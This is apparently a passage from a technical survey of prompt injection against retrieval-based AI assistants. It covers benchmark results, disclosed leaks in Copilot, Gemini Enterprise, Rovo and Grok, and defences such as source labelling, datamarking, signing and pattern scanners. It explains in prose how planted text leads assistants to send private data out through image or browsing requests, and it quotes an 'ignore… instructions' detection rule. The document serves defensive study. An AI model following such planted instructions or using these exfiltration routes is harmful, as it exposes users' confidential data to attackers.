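The planted paragraph in the shop example describes a filing step that a real company might have, without telling the assistant to ignore its rules or steal anything. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that the most effective real attacks increasingly resemble social engineering, the tricks fraudsters use on employees. Its example is an email, reported by outside researchers in 2025, that looked like routine follow-up on a staff restructuring and asked for an employee's details to be sent to a supposed compliance system. The attack worked in 50% of tests with one particular request from the user. According to OpenAI, attacks on ChatGPT most often try to send secrets from a conversation to a third party, and most of those it knows of fail because the model refuses.

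Rahman and Kim (2026), in *The Framing Gap*, measured how much wording matters in a setup close to the shop example. Their agent held a made-up secret token, was told to send it to only one trusted address, and had a web-posting tool that recorded each attempt without sending anything. For each attack, they ran the agent once on a clean page and once on a poisoned one, and counted a success only if the token leaked with the poisoned page but not with the clean one. Ten kinds of openly worded attack all had a 0% success rate against GPT-4o, but some wordings that presented the same leak as a routine part of handling data succeeded every time.

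Small changes in wording had large effects. Success rates for five paraphrases of one successful attack ranged from 0% to 100% and averaged 52%. An attacker who tried three of them would have succeeded about 96% of the time. But 13 newly written pages that also used routine wording, with other pretexts, failed in all 130 trials. An average success rate therefore poorly predicts how a single planted page will perform.

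Telling the agent to keep the token private made little difference. Without that instruction, the success rate of the routine-sounding attacks rose only from 31.9% to 38.1%, which is within the variation between repeated runs. Rahman and Kim conclude that the model had never connected the rule with what the page asked for, rather than being talked out of it. A broader rule against sending the token in any form cut the rate to zero, but a version that only listed specific behaviours left it at 48.8%. The attacks failed in all 48 valid trials on the ChatGPT product, but the researchers couldn't tell why because they couldn't see its internal safeguards.

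More recent models show a similar pattern. In *ClawSafety*, Wei, Zhang and colleagues (2026) built 120 simulated office cases in software, finance, healthcare, law and server operations. In each case, the planted text appeared in a web page, an email from a colleague, or an instruction file that the agent reads as an operating procedure. Conversations ran for up to 64 turns, and the agent met the planted text after about 45. The table gives the percentage of cases in which the agent, running on OpenClaw, fully completed the harmful action.

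| Model | Overall | Web page | Email | Instruction file |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.1 | 75.0 | 60.0 | 75.0 | 90.0 |
| DeepSeek V3 | 67.5 | 52.5 | 67.5 | 82.5 |
| Kimi K2.5 | 60.8 | 45.0 | 60.0 | 77.5 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 55.0 | 37.5 | 55.0 | 72.5 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 40.0 | 20.0 | 45.0 | 55.0 |

All five models were more likely to follow text from sources that an employee would trust more. Wei and colleagues didn't test documents retrieved from a company corpus, so this is a guess, but the models would probably follow a page that looks like the shop's own refund policy more often than a stranger's web page.

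The researchers refined these attacks over many failed versions, including 23 rounds for the web pages, so a typical attacker would succeed less often. Success also depends on the agent framework. Running Sonnet 4.6 on a different framework raised the success rate of the email attacks from 45.0% to 62.5%.

Individual cases suggest what made requests hard to refuse. A precise request from the treasurer, who was responsible for the payment in question, got Sonnet 4.6 to reveal confidential values, while a vaguer one from the higher-ranking finance chief failed. Requests to add an item to a report the agent was already writing succeeded much more often than requests for something new, such as forwarding a file. Familiarity also helped, as the agent leaked all 40 planted secrets in eight cases with named colleagues, but 19 when job titles replaced the names.

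In three server-operations cases with the same delivery and styling, Sonnet 4.6 recognised two commands to update a record as suspicious, although one of its warnings repeated the attacker's value. In the third case, the page gave no command and only stated that two values didn't match, and the agent copied this false finding into a report for a vice-president. Three cases on one model are weak evidence for a general rule, but they fit the concern from the first section that a search for commands will miss some planted text.

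Longer conversations give an attacker more to steal, and they also made the agents easier to mislead. On eight finance cases, the attack's success rate against Sonnet 4.6 rose from 50.0% in 10-turn conversations to 77.5% in 64-turn ones, and against GPT-5.1 it rose from 75.0% to 95.0%.

The overall rates hide the result most relevant to the shop's assistant. While developing the attacks, Wei and colleagues never got Sonnet 4.6 to send data to an address outside the workspace's known contacts, however they framed the request. In the finished benchmark, it never forwarded credentials to an unauthorised address, while GPT-5.1 did so in at least 60% of cases. Only 15 of the 120 cases tested this. Sonnet 4.6 would therefore probably refuse to post the conversation to attacker.example. Yet in 65% of the cases designed to make it do so, it still put protected data into reports, email drafts and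 similar documents, which an attacker with access to them could read without a webhook.

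## Which products have leaked data this way?

Between June 2025 and August 2026, security researchers published at least six attacks in which a commercial AI assistant followed an outsider's instructions and leaked private data. The products came from Microsoft, Google, Atlassian and xAI. In EchoLeak and GeminiJack, the assistant's own search found the planted instructions, as in the shop example. In the other four, the victim brought them in by clicking a link, uploading a file or asking the assistant to read a web page.

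| Attack | Product | How the instructions reached the model | What carried the data out | Status |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Copilot retrieved a planted email | Image request | Fixed in May 2025 |
| GeminiJack | Google Gemini Enterprise | Gemini retrieved a planted document, email or invitation | Image request | Fixed by November 2025 |
| SearchLeak | Microsoft 365 Copilot | The user clicked a link | Image request | Fixed by June 2026 |
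| RovoBlast | Atlassian Rovo | The user clicked a link | Image request | Fixed in July 2026 |
| Rovo file attack | Atlassian Rovo | The user uploaded a file | Rovo's tool for opening web addresses | Still worked when published on August 5, 2026 |
| Grok page attack | xAI Grok | The user asked for a summary of a web page | Grok's browsing tool | Still worked on August 19, 2026 |

Only EchoLeak and GeminiJack are cases of corpus poisoning. A scanner that checked retrieved chunks could not have stopped the other four, because their instructions didn't come from the corpus.

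### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their mailboxes, files and Teams chats. Aim Labs, then the research arm of Aim Security, found that an outsider could steal data from it by sending an employee an email. The email could come from any address, as Ravia (2025) explains in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*. The instructions in the email read like a request to the employee and never mentioned AI.

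The email stayed in the mailbox until the employee asked Copilot a question that matched it. The researchers didn't know which embedding model Microsoft used for Copilot, so they couldn't tune the email's text to it. Instead they wrote a long email with sections on several common office subjects, such as staff leave, so that its chunks would match a range of questions. Copilot retrieved it for questions on various topics, although Ravia gives no exposure rate.

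Copilot then wrote an answer containing an image whose address included sensitive information from the context. That information could include earlier chat messages or the contents of internal files. The employee's browser requested the image automatically, which sent the data out.

Microsoft had three defences that should have prevented this, and the attack passed all of them:

- An injection classifier, which is a type of scanner, checks text before it reaches Copilot's model. It didn't flag the email, which looked like a message from one person to another.
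- A filter removes links to outside sites from Copilot's answers. It missed links and images written in a less common format.
- An allow-list limits the domains from which the browser may load images. It included a Microsoft Teams service that fetches outside addresses on request, and this service passed the data to the attacker.

Each defence checked for a common sign of an attack, either suspicious wording, an outside link or an unfamiliar domain. None checked whether private data was going to an outsider, so the researchers could change the wording, the format and the domain and still steal the same data. Ravia argues that the real warning sign was an email from outside the company telling the model to use information from inside it. But he acknowledges that such an email is hard to detect, because its instructions could be meant for a person.

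The defences made the attack harder to build. After bypassing only the classifier and the link filter, the researchers still needed the employee to click a link. One way around the allow-list required the employee to accept an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site, but using the Teams service removed that step. The email also contained an instruction for Copilot not to mention it as a source, so the employee had little chance of noticing the attack.

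Aim Labs told Microsoft about the flaw in January 2025, and Microsoft finished the fix in May, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025). Microsoft made the change on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that Copilot now strips images and the less common type of link from outside content. This case study is by two George Washington University researchers who had no part in the discovery and rely on Aim Labs' account of it. Microsoft also reportedly added options to stop Copilot from using outside messages in some situations.

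Aim Labs published its findings on June 11, 2025. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* gives the flaw's severity score as 9.3 out of 10 and reports that Microsoft said no attacker had exploited it.

Ravia calls EchoLeak the first "zero-click" flaw in a major AI application, meaning that the victim doesn't have to click anything, though they still have to ask Copilot a question. Willison (2025) calls it an extended variant of earlier attacks. Both descriptions are fair, because putting stolen data in a web address was already a familiar method, but many earlier demonstrations required the user to click a link or point the chatbot at the malicious content.

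### GeminiJack

Gemini Enterprise, Google's assistant for companies, can search an organisation's Gmail, Calendar, Docs and other connected sources. Noma Security found that an outsider could plant instructions in any of these. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* describes an attack in which the outsider shares a document containing hidden instructions. An email or calendar invitation would also work. According to Noma, quoted in SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Gemini Enterprise Vulnerability Exposing Corporate Data*, the attacker could share the document without a notification, so the employee might never know it was there.

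When an employee later asked to see the company's budgets, Gemini would retrieve a planted document about budgets. The document's instructions made Gemini also search every connected source the employee was allowed to see for words such as "confidential", "salary" or "API key". Gemini put the results in an image address, and the employee's browser sent them to the attacker when it tried to load the image. The employee still received the budget information.

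It is less clear which defences failed against GeminiJack than against EchoLeak. Security Affairs' *GeminiJack zero-click flaw in Gemini Enterprise allowed corporate data exfiltration* quotes Noma's report that the attack triggered no traditional security tools. This isn't surprising, because browsers request images constantly. The AI Agent Index's entry *Gemini Enterprise* lists a built-in guardrail, Model Armor, that screens users' prompts and Gemini's responses for injection and sensitive data. It's unclear whether Model Armor was active in Noma's tests. Checking the user's prompt would have found only a harmless question about budgets, but checking the response could in principle have caught the stolen data.

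Noma reported the flaw in June 2025 according to most accounts, though SecurityWeek gives May. According to SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise*, Noma and Google resolved it by November, and Noma published its report in December. Google confirmed to SecurityWeek that Noma had described the flaw accurately and that Google had fixed it.

Infosecurity Magazine reports that Google changed how Gemini Enterprise works with its retrieval and indexing systems. Google also separated it from Vertex AI Search, a related product that had the same weakness. In its report, Noma probably gave the fix too much credit for addressing the underlying confusion between instructions and content, since no known method removes this confusion from a language model. Noma's research lead, Sasi Levi, told SC Media that Google hadn't disclosed the technical details.

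No source reports that anyone used GeminiJack to steal data. For this reason, the OECD's *Google GeminiJack AI Vulnerability Exposes Corporate Data* (2025), an entry in the organization's AI incident monitor, classes it as a hazard. The monitor works from news articles, so the classification is not the result of an investigation.

### SearchLeak

A year after EchoLeak, researchers got data out of Copilot again, this time without planting anything in a mailbox. *SearchLeak* (2026), by the data-security company Varonis, describes an attack on Copilot's enterprise search that began with a link. The link led to Microsoft's real website, so anti-phishing tools had no basis for blocking it. It also contained instructions, and when the victim clicked it, Copilot followed them as though the victim had typed them.

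The attacker therefore didn't have to compete for a place in the search results. Copilot ran searches on the attacker's behalf and could look through the victim's mail, calendar and company files. In the demonstration, the attack stole an email's subject line, which can be valuable because subject lines often contain login codes.

As in EchoLeak, the data left in an image address, and Microsoft's defences failed in two places. Copilot's software converts any code in an answer to plain text, which would have made the image harmless, but it did this only once the answer was complete. The browser displayed the answer as Copilot wrote it, so it had already requested the image by then.

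The allow-list should have blocked that request, but it included Bing, whose image search fetches outside addresses on request. EchoLeak had used a Teams service in the same way. Bing was already on the allow-list that Ravia printed in 2025, so closing one such service left another available. An allow-list of domains is safe only if no approved service will forward data to an unapproved address, and Microsoft runs many services.

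Varonis' later report, *RovoBlast* (2026), points out that the assistant in SearchLeak had no direct internet access, so the victim's browser alone met Willison's condition of external communication.

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), published on June 4, states that the company had fully mitigated the flaw and that nobody had exploited it. Microsoft rated the flaw critical but scored it 6.5, compared with 9.3 for EchoLeak, partly because the victim had to click.

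### Two routes into Rovo

Rovo is Atlassian's assistant for Jira, which companies use to track work, and Confluence, where they keep internal documents. Two security firms published attacks on it in August 2026.

RovoBlast, an attack on Atlassian's Rovo that Varonis found, worked much like SearchLeak. A link to Atlassian's own site contained the instructions, and one click made Rovo follow them using the victim's permissions. Companies can connect Rovo to services such as Slack, Google Workspace and Microsoft 365, so a single account may reach a lot of data. The Hacker News (2026) reports that the demonstration took a private access key from Confluence and sent it out in an image URL. Varonis also identified a research feature that could browse any website as another possible way to send data out.

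Varonis found few defences to get past, and Rovo showed no warning that the prompt had come from a link. Atlassian fixed the flaw on its servers on July 8 and paid a $6,000 reward through Bugcrowd, a service researchers use to report flaws to companies.

In the other attack, described in PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, a user uploads a document with hidden instructions and asks Rovo to organise some Jira tickets. Rovo searches Jira and Confluence for the task, adds what it finds to an attacker's web address, and opens the address with its tool for retrieving pages. Rovo doesn't ask the user to approve this step, and a user who returns to the chat later sees only the suggested ticket changes.

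The company in the demonstration had switched off web search for Rovo, but this didn't stop the leak because the setting left the page-retrieval tool on. An administrator might reasonably expect the setting to cut the assistant off from the internet. Nothing checked whether Rovo had composed the address itself.

This attack is closer to corpus poisoning than the ones that used links. PromptArmor says the same instructions could arrive in a support ticket or through a connected service, without the victim uploading anything. PromptArmor demonstrated only the upload, so those other routes are plausible but unproven.

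A post on Atlassian Community, the company's user forum, had said that a file with hidden instructions couldn't trick Rovo, because Rovo filters and scans files and treats their text as content. The post isn't an official statement, and the demonstration contradicts it.

PromptArmor reported the flaw to Atlassian on May 23, 2026 and received a case number two days later. Atlassian didn't respond to further messages in June and July, and the attack still worked when PromptArmor published on August 5. The Hacker News found no update three days later and couldn't determine whether the July fix for links had any effect on files.

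Until Atlassian confirms a fix, customers' main option is to limit what Rovo can read. Varonis says customers can't fully uninstall it. According to The Hacker News, administrators can block Rovo for individual apps, but on a site with several Jira apps, its search and chat stay available if any of those apps has Rovo enabled. Neither firm reports that anyone has used its attack against a real organisation.

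### Chat histories from Grok

Adversa AI's *Zero-click Grok data theft* (2026) describes a leak from Grok, xAI's chatbot, that starts when a user asks it to summarise a web page the attacker controls. Grok reads the page, then uses its browsing tool to open an address containing the user's name, approximate location, subscription tier and everything the user has typed in the conversation. It doesn't warn the user or ask for confirmation.

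The page carried its instructions in a form that text filters couldn't read, and Adversa AI withheld the working version. A better filter might catch instructions hidden this way. The more basic weakness was that text from an untrusted page could make Grok send private data to any address, and Adversa AI found no effective control to prevent that.

Adversa AI reported the flaw to xAI on June 3, 2026. xAI acknowledged the report without giving a date for a fix, and didn't reply to two more contact attempts in August. The attack still worked on August 19. Adversa AI doesn't describe any thefts from real users.

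*Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok*, a 2024 report by the researcher behind Embrace The Red, had already shown that Grok in the X app for iPhone could send chat content to an outside server by loading an image. Willison (2024) noted that xAI had closed all the report's issues as "Informational", a label companies use for findings they don't intend to treat as flaws.

### Are criminals using these attacks?

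None of the companies or researchers involved in these six cases reports a theft by criminals. Microsoft states that nobody exploited EchoLeak or SearchLeak. For the other four, the only evidence against exploitation is the lack of reports.

Microsoft's statements are somewhat credible because the stolen data passed through its own servers on the way out, which may have left records it could search. A victim would have had much less evidence and could easily have missed the theft. The EchoLeak email contained instructions for Copilot not to mention it, GeminiJack's victim received a normal answer, and Rovo's chat showed no trace of the attack afterwards.

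Attackers also had time to find the flaws themselves. EchoLeak was fully fixed about four months after Aim Labs reported it, and GeminiJack about five months after it was reported. The Rovo file attack still worked 74 days after PromptArmor reported it, and the Grok attack still worked 77 days after Adversa AI reported it.

There is better evidence of attempts than of successful thefts. Khodayari and colleagues found a few planted instructions of this kind on the open web, and OpenAI has seen attempts against ChatGPT, but neither has documented a successful theft from a company's document collection. As of late 2026, the public evidence is enough to treat this as a proven weakness that people have tried to exploit, but not to estimate how much criminals have stolen.

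### How far to trust the finders

Most of the companies that found these flaws sell protection against them, and alarming names and claims to be first help sell such products. Ravia ends by recommending Aim Labs' guardrails, and Adversa AI reports that its platform stopped the Grok attack when the company tested the attack on a coding agent. PromptArmor sells monitoring of suppliers' AI products, and Varonis offers readers a demonstration of its software.

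This seems to have affected how the attacks were labeled more than the facts reported. PromptArmor called its Rovo attack "zero-click", for example, but The Hacker News objected that the victim still has to give Rovo the poisoned file and make a request. Google confirmed Noma's account, Microsoft published formal records of its flaws, and Atlassian accepted and paid for the report on links. The Rovo file attack and the Grok attack have less support because neither vendor has publicly confirmed them. But vendors also have reasons to play flaws down, so their silence isn't strong evidence against the finders.

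The reports give much less information about how often such attacks would work. Each shows that an attack succeeded, but none gives the number of attempts, the share of questions that retrieved the planted text, or how often the model refused. Researchers also publish successful attacks but rarely report which products withstood them. The EchoLeak and GeminiJack cases therefore show that all three probabilities in the formula for a leak were above zero, but we can't estimate their values from these reports.

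## Does labelling retrieved text with its source protect the model?

Software can catch an attack like EchoLeak by its origin only if it knows which passages came from outside the company when it assembles the context. A provenance wrapper keeps this information attached to a retrieved chunk, using markers and metadata that identify the chunk's source and label it as data, not instructions.

A wrapper that labels a retrieved passage with its source marks the passage as data, but the model may still follow instructions in it. The label also lets the surrounding software apply rules based on the passage's source, such as blocking web requests while an outsider's text is in the context. The software applies these rules every time, however persuasive the passage is. Most experiments have measured only the wrapper's effect on the model, which has ranged from near-complete protection to none.

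### What a wrapper should record

A wrapper for the planted chunk in the shop example, from the reseller's "Refund policy" page, could carry these fields:

| Field | Value for the planted chunk | What the software can do with it |
|---|---|---|
| Source | "Refund policy", reseller pages | Show staff where an answer came from |
| Author | Reseller account 2081 | Find everything else from the same account |
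| Route and date of entry | Reseller upload form, March 3 | Withdraw whatever arrived by that route since a given day |
| Content hash | 9f3c… | Notice if someone edits the page later |
| Trust level | Low (outside party) | Rank the chunk lower, or stop it from triggering tool calls |
| Scan result | Nothing found, March 3 | Scan again when the text or the scanner changes |

A content hash is a short code computed from the text, and it changes if anyone alters the text. The title suggests that the shop wrote the page, but an attacker can put any title or byline in a document, so the trust level has to come from the account that uploaded the page.

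Many systems lose track of where retrieved text came from because a simple index returns only the text. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) recommends that retrieval systems preserve provenance past the vector search, and that software label untrusted content and limit what that content can authorise. Preserving provenance is simple in a basic system, where the indexing program copies the document's fields to each chunk and stores them beside the vector.

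### Three ways to mark text for the model

Hines, Lopez and colleagues (2024), in *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting*, developed the best-known way of telling the model which text is data. Spotlighting changes the untrusted text before the model sees it. The system instructions then explain the change and say not to follow any instructions in text that has it. The Microsoft researchers described three forms, shown here on a line from a refund page:

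```
original:       Refunds take 30 days
delimiters:     <<Refunds take 30 days>>
datamarking:    Refunds^take^30^days
encoding:       UmVmdW5kcyB0YWtlIDMwIGRheXM=
```

Delimiters mark only the beginning and end of the passage. Datamarking replaces every space with a special character, so the mark runs through the whole text. Encoding rewrites the passage in base64, a standard way of representing data with 64 plain characters. A capable model can read base64 without a separate decoding step.

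To test these, the researchers generated 1,000 documents containing an instruction to drop the task and reply with a single keyword. They used OpenAI models from 2023 or earlier. With GPT-3.5-Turbo summarising the documents, the attack succeeded 50–60% of the time. A warning in the system instructions barely changed that rate, and adding delimiters cut it by about half. Datamarking cut it to 3.1%, and encoding to 0.0%. Datamarking also reduced the attack's success rate against text-davinci-003 from 40% to 0.0%. When the task was answering questions about a document, the attack's success rates with datamarking were 8.0% for GPT-3.5-Turbo, 1.0% for GPT-4 and 0.0% for text-davinci-003.

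The reductions are large, but the test was easier for the model than the attack in the shop example. Hines and colleagues counted an attack as successful only when the planted instruction took over the whole reply, so a model that summarised the document and also mentioned the keyword counted as having resisted. An assistant that leaks a conversation usually also answers the user's question. The researchers report the same trends under a looser count, but they didn't test data theft.

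### Marking on newer models

*Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (Shi, Lin and colleagues, 2025) reports Google DeepMind's test of datamarking as a defence against data theft. The researchers inserted a special token after every eight characters of retrieved text, including an email's sender and subject line. The planted text was meant to make Gemini send the user's passport number to the attacker, and the researchers used three automated methods to search for wordings that worked. The table gives the range of attack success rates across the three methods, for attacks developed without the defence in place.

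| Model | No defence | With marking |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 1.5 Flash | 82–98% | 0–3% |
| Gemini 1.5 Pro | 88–99% | 3–33% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 97–100% | 13–75% |

The Gemini 2.0 tests planted the text in a calendar event instead of an email, so the rows aren't strictly comparable. Still, a defence that looked almost perfect on one model was weak on its successor. Attacks tuned to the marking succeeded against Gemini 2.0 in 65–82% of cases. Shi and colleagues conclude that each new model version needs fresh tests.

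When Shi and colleagues varied the settings, they found that the inserted tokens mainly interrupt the way the model splits the planted text into tokens, so the model is less likely to read it as an instruction. Marking seems to work largely by damaging the attack rather than by teaching the model where the text came from. They therefore expect it to do little against attacks in Chinese or Japanese, where a single character can carry the meaning of a word.

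It also roughly doubles the number of tokens in the marked sections. This added 100–200 tokens to a typical tool-use prompt in Google's data, but a RAG system that retrieves five chunks of 300 tokens would add about 1,500 to every question.

On Gemini 2.0, a plain warning worked better than marking the retrieved text. Shi and colleagues put an instruction not to reveal the user's private information after the retrieved text, just before the model's reply, and the same kind of attacks succeeded in 0.2–5.8% of cases. But users sometimes want an agent to share private information, for instance to fill in a visa form.

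Delimiters were the weakest form of labelling in 2024, and results since then have been mixed. In *RAISED*, Dhouib, Elliker and colleagues (2026) compared them with four other defences: repeating the user's task after every tool result, Meta's injection scanner PromptGuard 2, and two methods that retrain the model, SecAlign++ and RAISED. They used AgentDojo, a standard set of simulated office, banking, travel and messaging tasks with instructions planted in the tool results. The table gives attack success rates in percent.

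| Defence | Gemma 4 12B | Nemotron 3 Nano 30B | Qwen3.8 27B |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 39.5 | 11.7 | 5.8 |
| Delimiters | 43.9 | 11.4 | 0.9 |
| Task repeated | 34.1 | 6.3 | 3.8 |
| PromptGuard 2 | 16.1 | 5.7 | 2.7 |
| SecAlign++ | 1.1 | 4.0 | 1.9 |
| RAISED | 1.0 | 0.5 | 0.9 |

Delimiters gave Gemma and Nemotron no useful protection, but they worked as well as retraining on Qwen. The pattern was the same on a second, harder benchmark. Under attack, Qwen also completed more of the users' tasks with delimiters (85.4%) than without (80.0%). A model may need to be good at following the operator's rules before a rule about markers can help it. Three models are too few to establish this, and the attack texts were not adapted to the defence.

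RAISED, the researchers' own method, needs no markers. It uses two copies of a model, one of them frozen. The frozen copy gets a clean tool result, and the other gets the same result with an instruction planted in it. Training pushes the second copy to predict the same next tokens as the frozen one, so it learns to ignore the planted text while still using the rest of the result.

Some retrieved text contains instructions that the agent should follow. In one of Dhouib and colleagues' examples, a user asks for a password change and the system emails a verification code. An agent retrained with an older method stopped at this step and asked the user for the code, even though it could have read the email. A wrapper that forbids the model to act on anything between the markers risks the same failure. For example, the shop's own returns page might instruct the assistant to ask for a photo of the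 damage first, which the shop wants it to do.

### How planted text gets past a label

An attacker who knows the closing marker can include it in the document, so that any text after it appears to be outside the marked passage. Hines and colleagues advise against fixed delimiters for this reason, and recommend assuming that attackers have seen the system instructions. A random marker generated for each request is much harder to copy, because a document planted earlier was written before the marker existed. The chance of guessing a marker of k characters drawn from a set of N is 1/N^k. *No More, No Less* (2026), a study of agents that work on a command line, used markers of twelve hexadecimal characters, which have about 281 trillion possible values.

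But a language model may accept a marker that isn't an exact match. Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026) studied planted text that imitates trusted data instead of giving orders in *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*. For example, the body of an email might contain what looks like the start of a second email from a trusted colleague. A conventional program would read this as part of the first email, particularly after the mail software had neutralised the punctuation, but the models often read it as a separate email. Across six models, such forgeries succeeded 31.3–43.3% of the time in JSON, a common format for tool results. Against agents with strong defences, planted instructions succeeded in at most 0.7% of attempts, while forged data succeeded in up to 50.0%.

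This is a serious problem for wrappers, because the attack imitates the kind of data their fields contain. The reseller's page could include what looks like a second wrapper naming the shop as the author. The fake wrapper would not affect the software, which stores the real fields separately, so it is safer for code to enforce the trust level than to print it in the context and rely on the model to weigh it.

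The model may also read a correct label and still obey the text, because the text's style tends to influence it more than the label does. Ye and colleagues found that a plain statement about where the text came from can also have more influence than a label. They placed the same command in 212 different templates, some of which included a statement that the text came from the user. These made up 24% of the templates but all of the top 5% when ranked by how strongly the model represented the command as the user's. A label wrapped around retrieved text is also a written claim about who is speaking, and an attacker can put a competing claim inside that text.

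*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) proves that if a marking is reversible, as it must be for the model to read the text, then some possible model reacts to the marked text exactly as it would to the raw text. A model that never follows instructions in marked text is safe, but the system's design cannot guarantee that the model behaves this way.

Source labels do not help against some planted text. *PARSE* (2026) notes that spotlighting provides no signal when an attack resembles ordinary document content. For example, an assistant could treat a false returns address strictly as data and still pass it on to the customer.

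Heavier marking can also make the model worse at its real task. Datamarking didn't reduce GPT-3.5-Turbo's scores on four standard language tests, but encoding reduced them badly because the model made mistakes while decoding. GPT-4 handled most encoded text well. On Gemini 1.5 Flash, marking left summaries of harmless emails as good as before, but two attack methods produced empty replies in 44% and 68% of cases. An empty reply is safer than a leak, but an attacker could use this to stop the assistant from answering. Even delimiters lowered Gemma's score on one set of harmless office tasks from 55.9% to 50.4%, although they raised it on another.

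Hines and colleagues compare the underlying problem to early telephone networks, which sent control signals and voices down the same line. Callers who could imitate the control tones made free calls until the companies moved the signals to a separate channel. Language models have no such channel, but two recent proposals try to approximate one. *LTBD* (2026) trains four delimiters as vectors and leaves the rest of the model unchanged. *Origin Is All You Need* (2026) attaches an origin label to each token and limits how far untrusted tokens can influence the output. Both require access to the model's internals, so a company that rents a model over the internet can't add them itself.

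### Checking origin when a document enters

What the software writes in the wrapper is only as reliable as the information it has. *RAGShield* (Patil, 2026) borrows a method from software distribution, where publishers sign their programs so that users can detect forgeries. Each document needs a signed record before it enters the corpus. The record contains a hash of the text, the source, a trust level, an identifier for the signing key, the time and the signature. RAGShield rejects documents with missing or invalid signatures, and also blocks a document if hidden content makes up more than 20% of it.

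The trust level τ runs from 1.0 for official legal texts through 0.8 for agency publications and 0.3 for public comments to 0.1 for unknown sources. The retriever multiplies it into the similarity score:

score(q, D) = sim(q, D) × τ^α

The setting α controls how strongly trust affects a chunk's score. In the earlier travel-expenses example, the attacker's tuned chunk scored 0.86 and ranked second. Suppose α = 1, and the company's own pages have a trust level of 0.8 while an outsider's have 0.3. The attacker's chunk then drops to 0.26 and ranks last, below the page on parental leave at 0.32.

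A system also has to preserve labels as it processes text. In RAGShield, each chunk inherits its document's trust level, the context takes the lowest level of any chunk in it, and the answer can't rank higher than the context. A single public comment among five chunks limits the whole answer to that comment's trust level. This is cautious, but it may leave few answers with a high rating. Other systems extend this kind of tracking to tool calls.

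Patil tested the design on 500 Wikipedia passages, 200 questions and several kinds of attacker. The table gives attack success rates in percent.

| Attacker | No defence | Signatures only | Full system |
|---|---|---|---|
| Outsider without a signature | 13.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| Outsider with a forged signature | 8.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| Insider with a valid signature | 8.0 | 8.0 | 0.0 |
| Text hidden in a file | 8.5 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
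| Insider who knows the defence | 11.0 | 11.0 | 0.0 |

Signatures stopped every outsider but had no effect on insiders. The full system stopped the insiders by comparing each new document's vector with those already in the corpus, looking for contradictions, missing corroboration and unusual claims. It failed to stop an insider who edited 20 existing documents instead of adding new ones. Each edit changed a single number, and the attack success rate was 17.5%. Patil proposes checking stored hashes, which would reveal such edits, but didn't test this.

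The content checks alone also scored 0.0% against all five attackers, so the experiment doesn't show that signatures added anything. Changing the thresholds, or setting α to zero so that trust had no effect on ranking, made no difference. Patil interprets this as robustness, but it could equally mean that the attacks were too easy. The corpus was tiny, the implementation only simulated the signatures, and the planted documents contained false facts, not instructions. Signatures keep out unsigned documents by design, but it is unknown how well the content checks would recognise a planted instruction.

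Another experiment shows how text can lose its label. *Poisoning Attacks and Collaborative Defense Framework for LightRAG-Based Construction Regulation Knowledge* (2026) tested a filter that excluded any document whose hash wasn't on an approved list. The filter kept every poisoned chunk out, but LightRAG also writes short descriptions of the people, things and rules it finds while indexing, and these went into the prompt unfiltered. Every attack that still succeeded did so through these descriptions. When the researchers added a genuine amendment that wasn't on the list, its wording reached the prompt the same way in 14 of 16 measurable cases. Summaries, translations and an agent's saved notes could also lose their labels unless the software copies the labels to everything it derives from a document.

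### A verified source can still supply an attack

The main objection to relying on provenance is that it shows who supplied a document but not whether it is harmless. An attacker who takes over a colleague's account can sign with the colleague's key. In the travel-expenses example, the tuned chunk would then get a trust level of 0.8, the same as the company's own pages, and return to second place.

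Outside text can be labelled as trusted without anyone breaking into an account. An employee may save a supplier's file to the shared drive, and a system that records only the last step will list the employee as the source. A rule that trusted everything in the workspace would also have trusted the document an outsider shared in GeminiJack. The system would catch both cases if it recorded every step the text took and applied the lowest trust level among them. But it would have no record of an employee copying a paragraph from a website into a policy page.

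Labelling a passage as untrusted is less risky than giving it a high trust label, which could help an attacker. The agents that Wei and colleagues tested followed instructions from more trusted kinds of source more often. Nobody seems to have tested whether a wrapper has the same effect, but labelling a colleague's hijacked page as authoritative is unlikely to protect the model.

Excluding everything with a low trust level isn't practical either. The approved list in the LightRAG study couldn't distinguish a poisoned new document from a genuine new amendment, the kind of document that users of building regulations most need to see. A support assistant likewise has to read customers' tickets, and an office assistant email from strangers. The origin of such text is weak evidence of whether it contains an attack, so the system also has to examine the text itself.

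## How does a scanner recognise an injected instruction?

A scanner checks a piece of text and returns either a verdict on whether it contains an injected instruction or a score for how likely that is. It can run when a document enters the corpus, so that each chunk needs only one scan. It can also run when the retriever returns a chunk, which requires a scan for every use but lets the scanner take the user's question into account. In both cases, it should run after the system has dealt with hidden text and invisible characters, so that it checks the same text the model receives.

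Recognising an instruction is fairly easy, but ordinary documents contain many instructions, so a scanner that flagged every one would withhold much of what an assistant needs.

### Pattern rules

A pattern rule searches the raw text for wording typical of known attacks. One rule might match "ignore" or "disregard" followed within a few words by "instructions", and another might match a verb such as "send" followed by a web address. Rules take almost no time to run, and staff can see exactly which words triggered a match.

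Munirathinam (2026), in *Beyond Pattern Matching*, ran the rules of an open-source scanner, prompt-shield, on 8,276 attack texts from three public benchmarks. The rules caught about 99% of attempts to extract data, because those texts contained something distinctive, such as the attacker's web address or an account number. They caught about 92% of attacks that openly told the model to drop its instructions, but only about 37% of subtler ones that read like legitimate requests. On another test set, made up mostly of paraphrased attacks, they caught 1 of 60.

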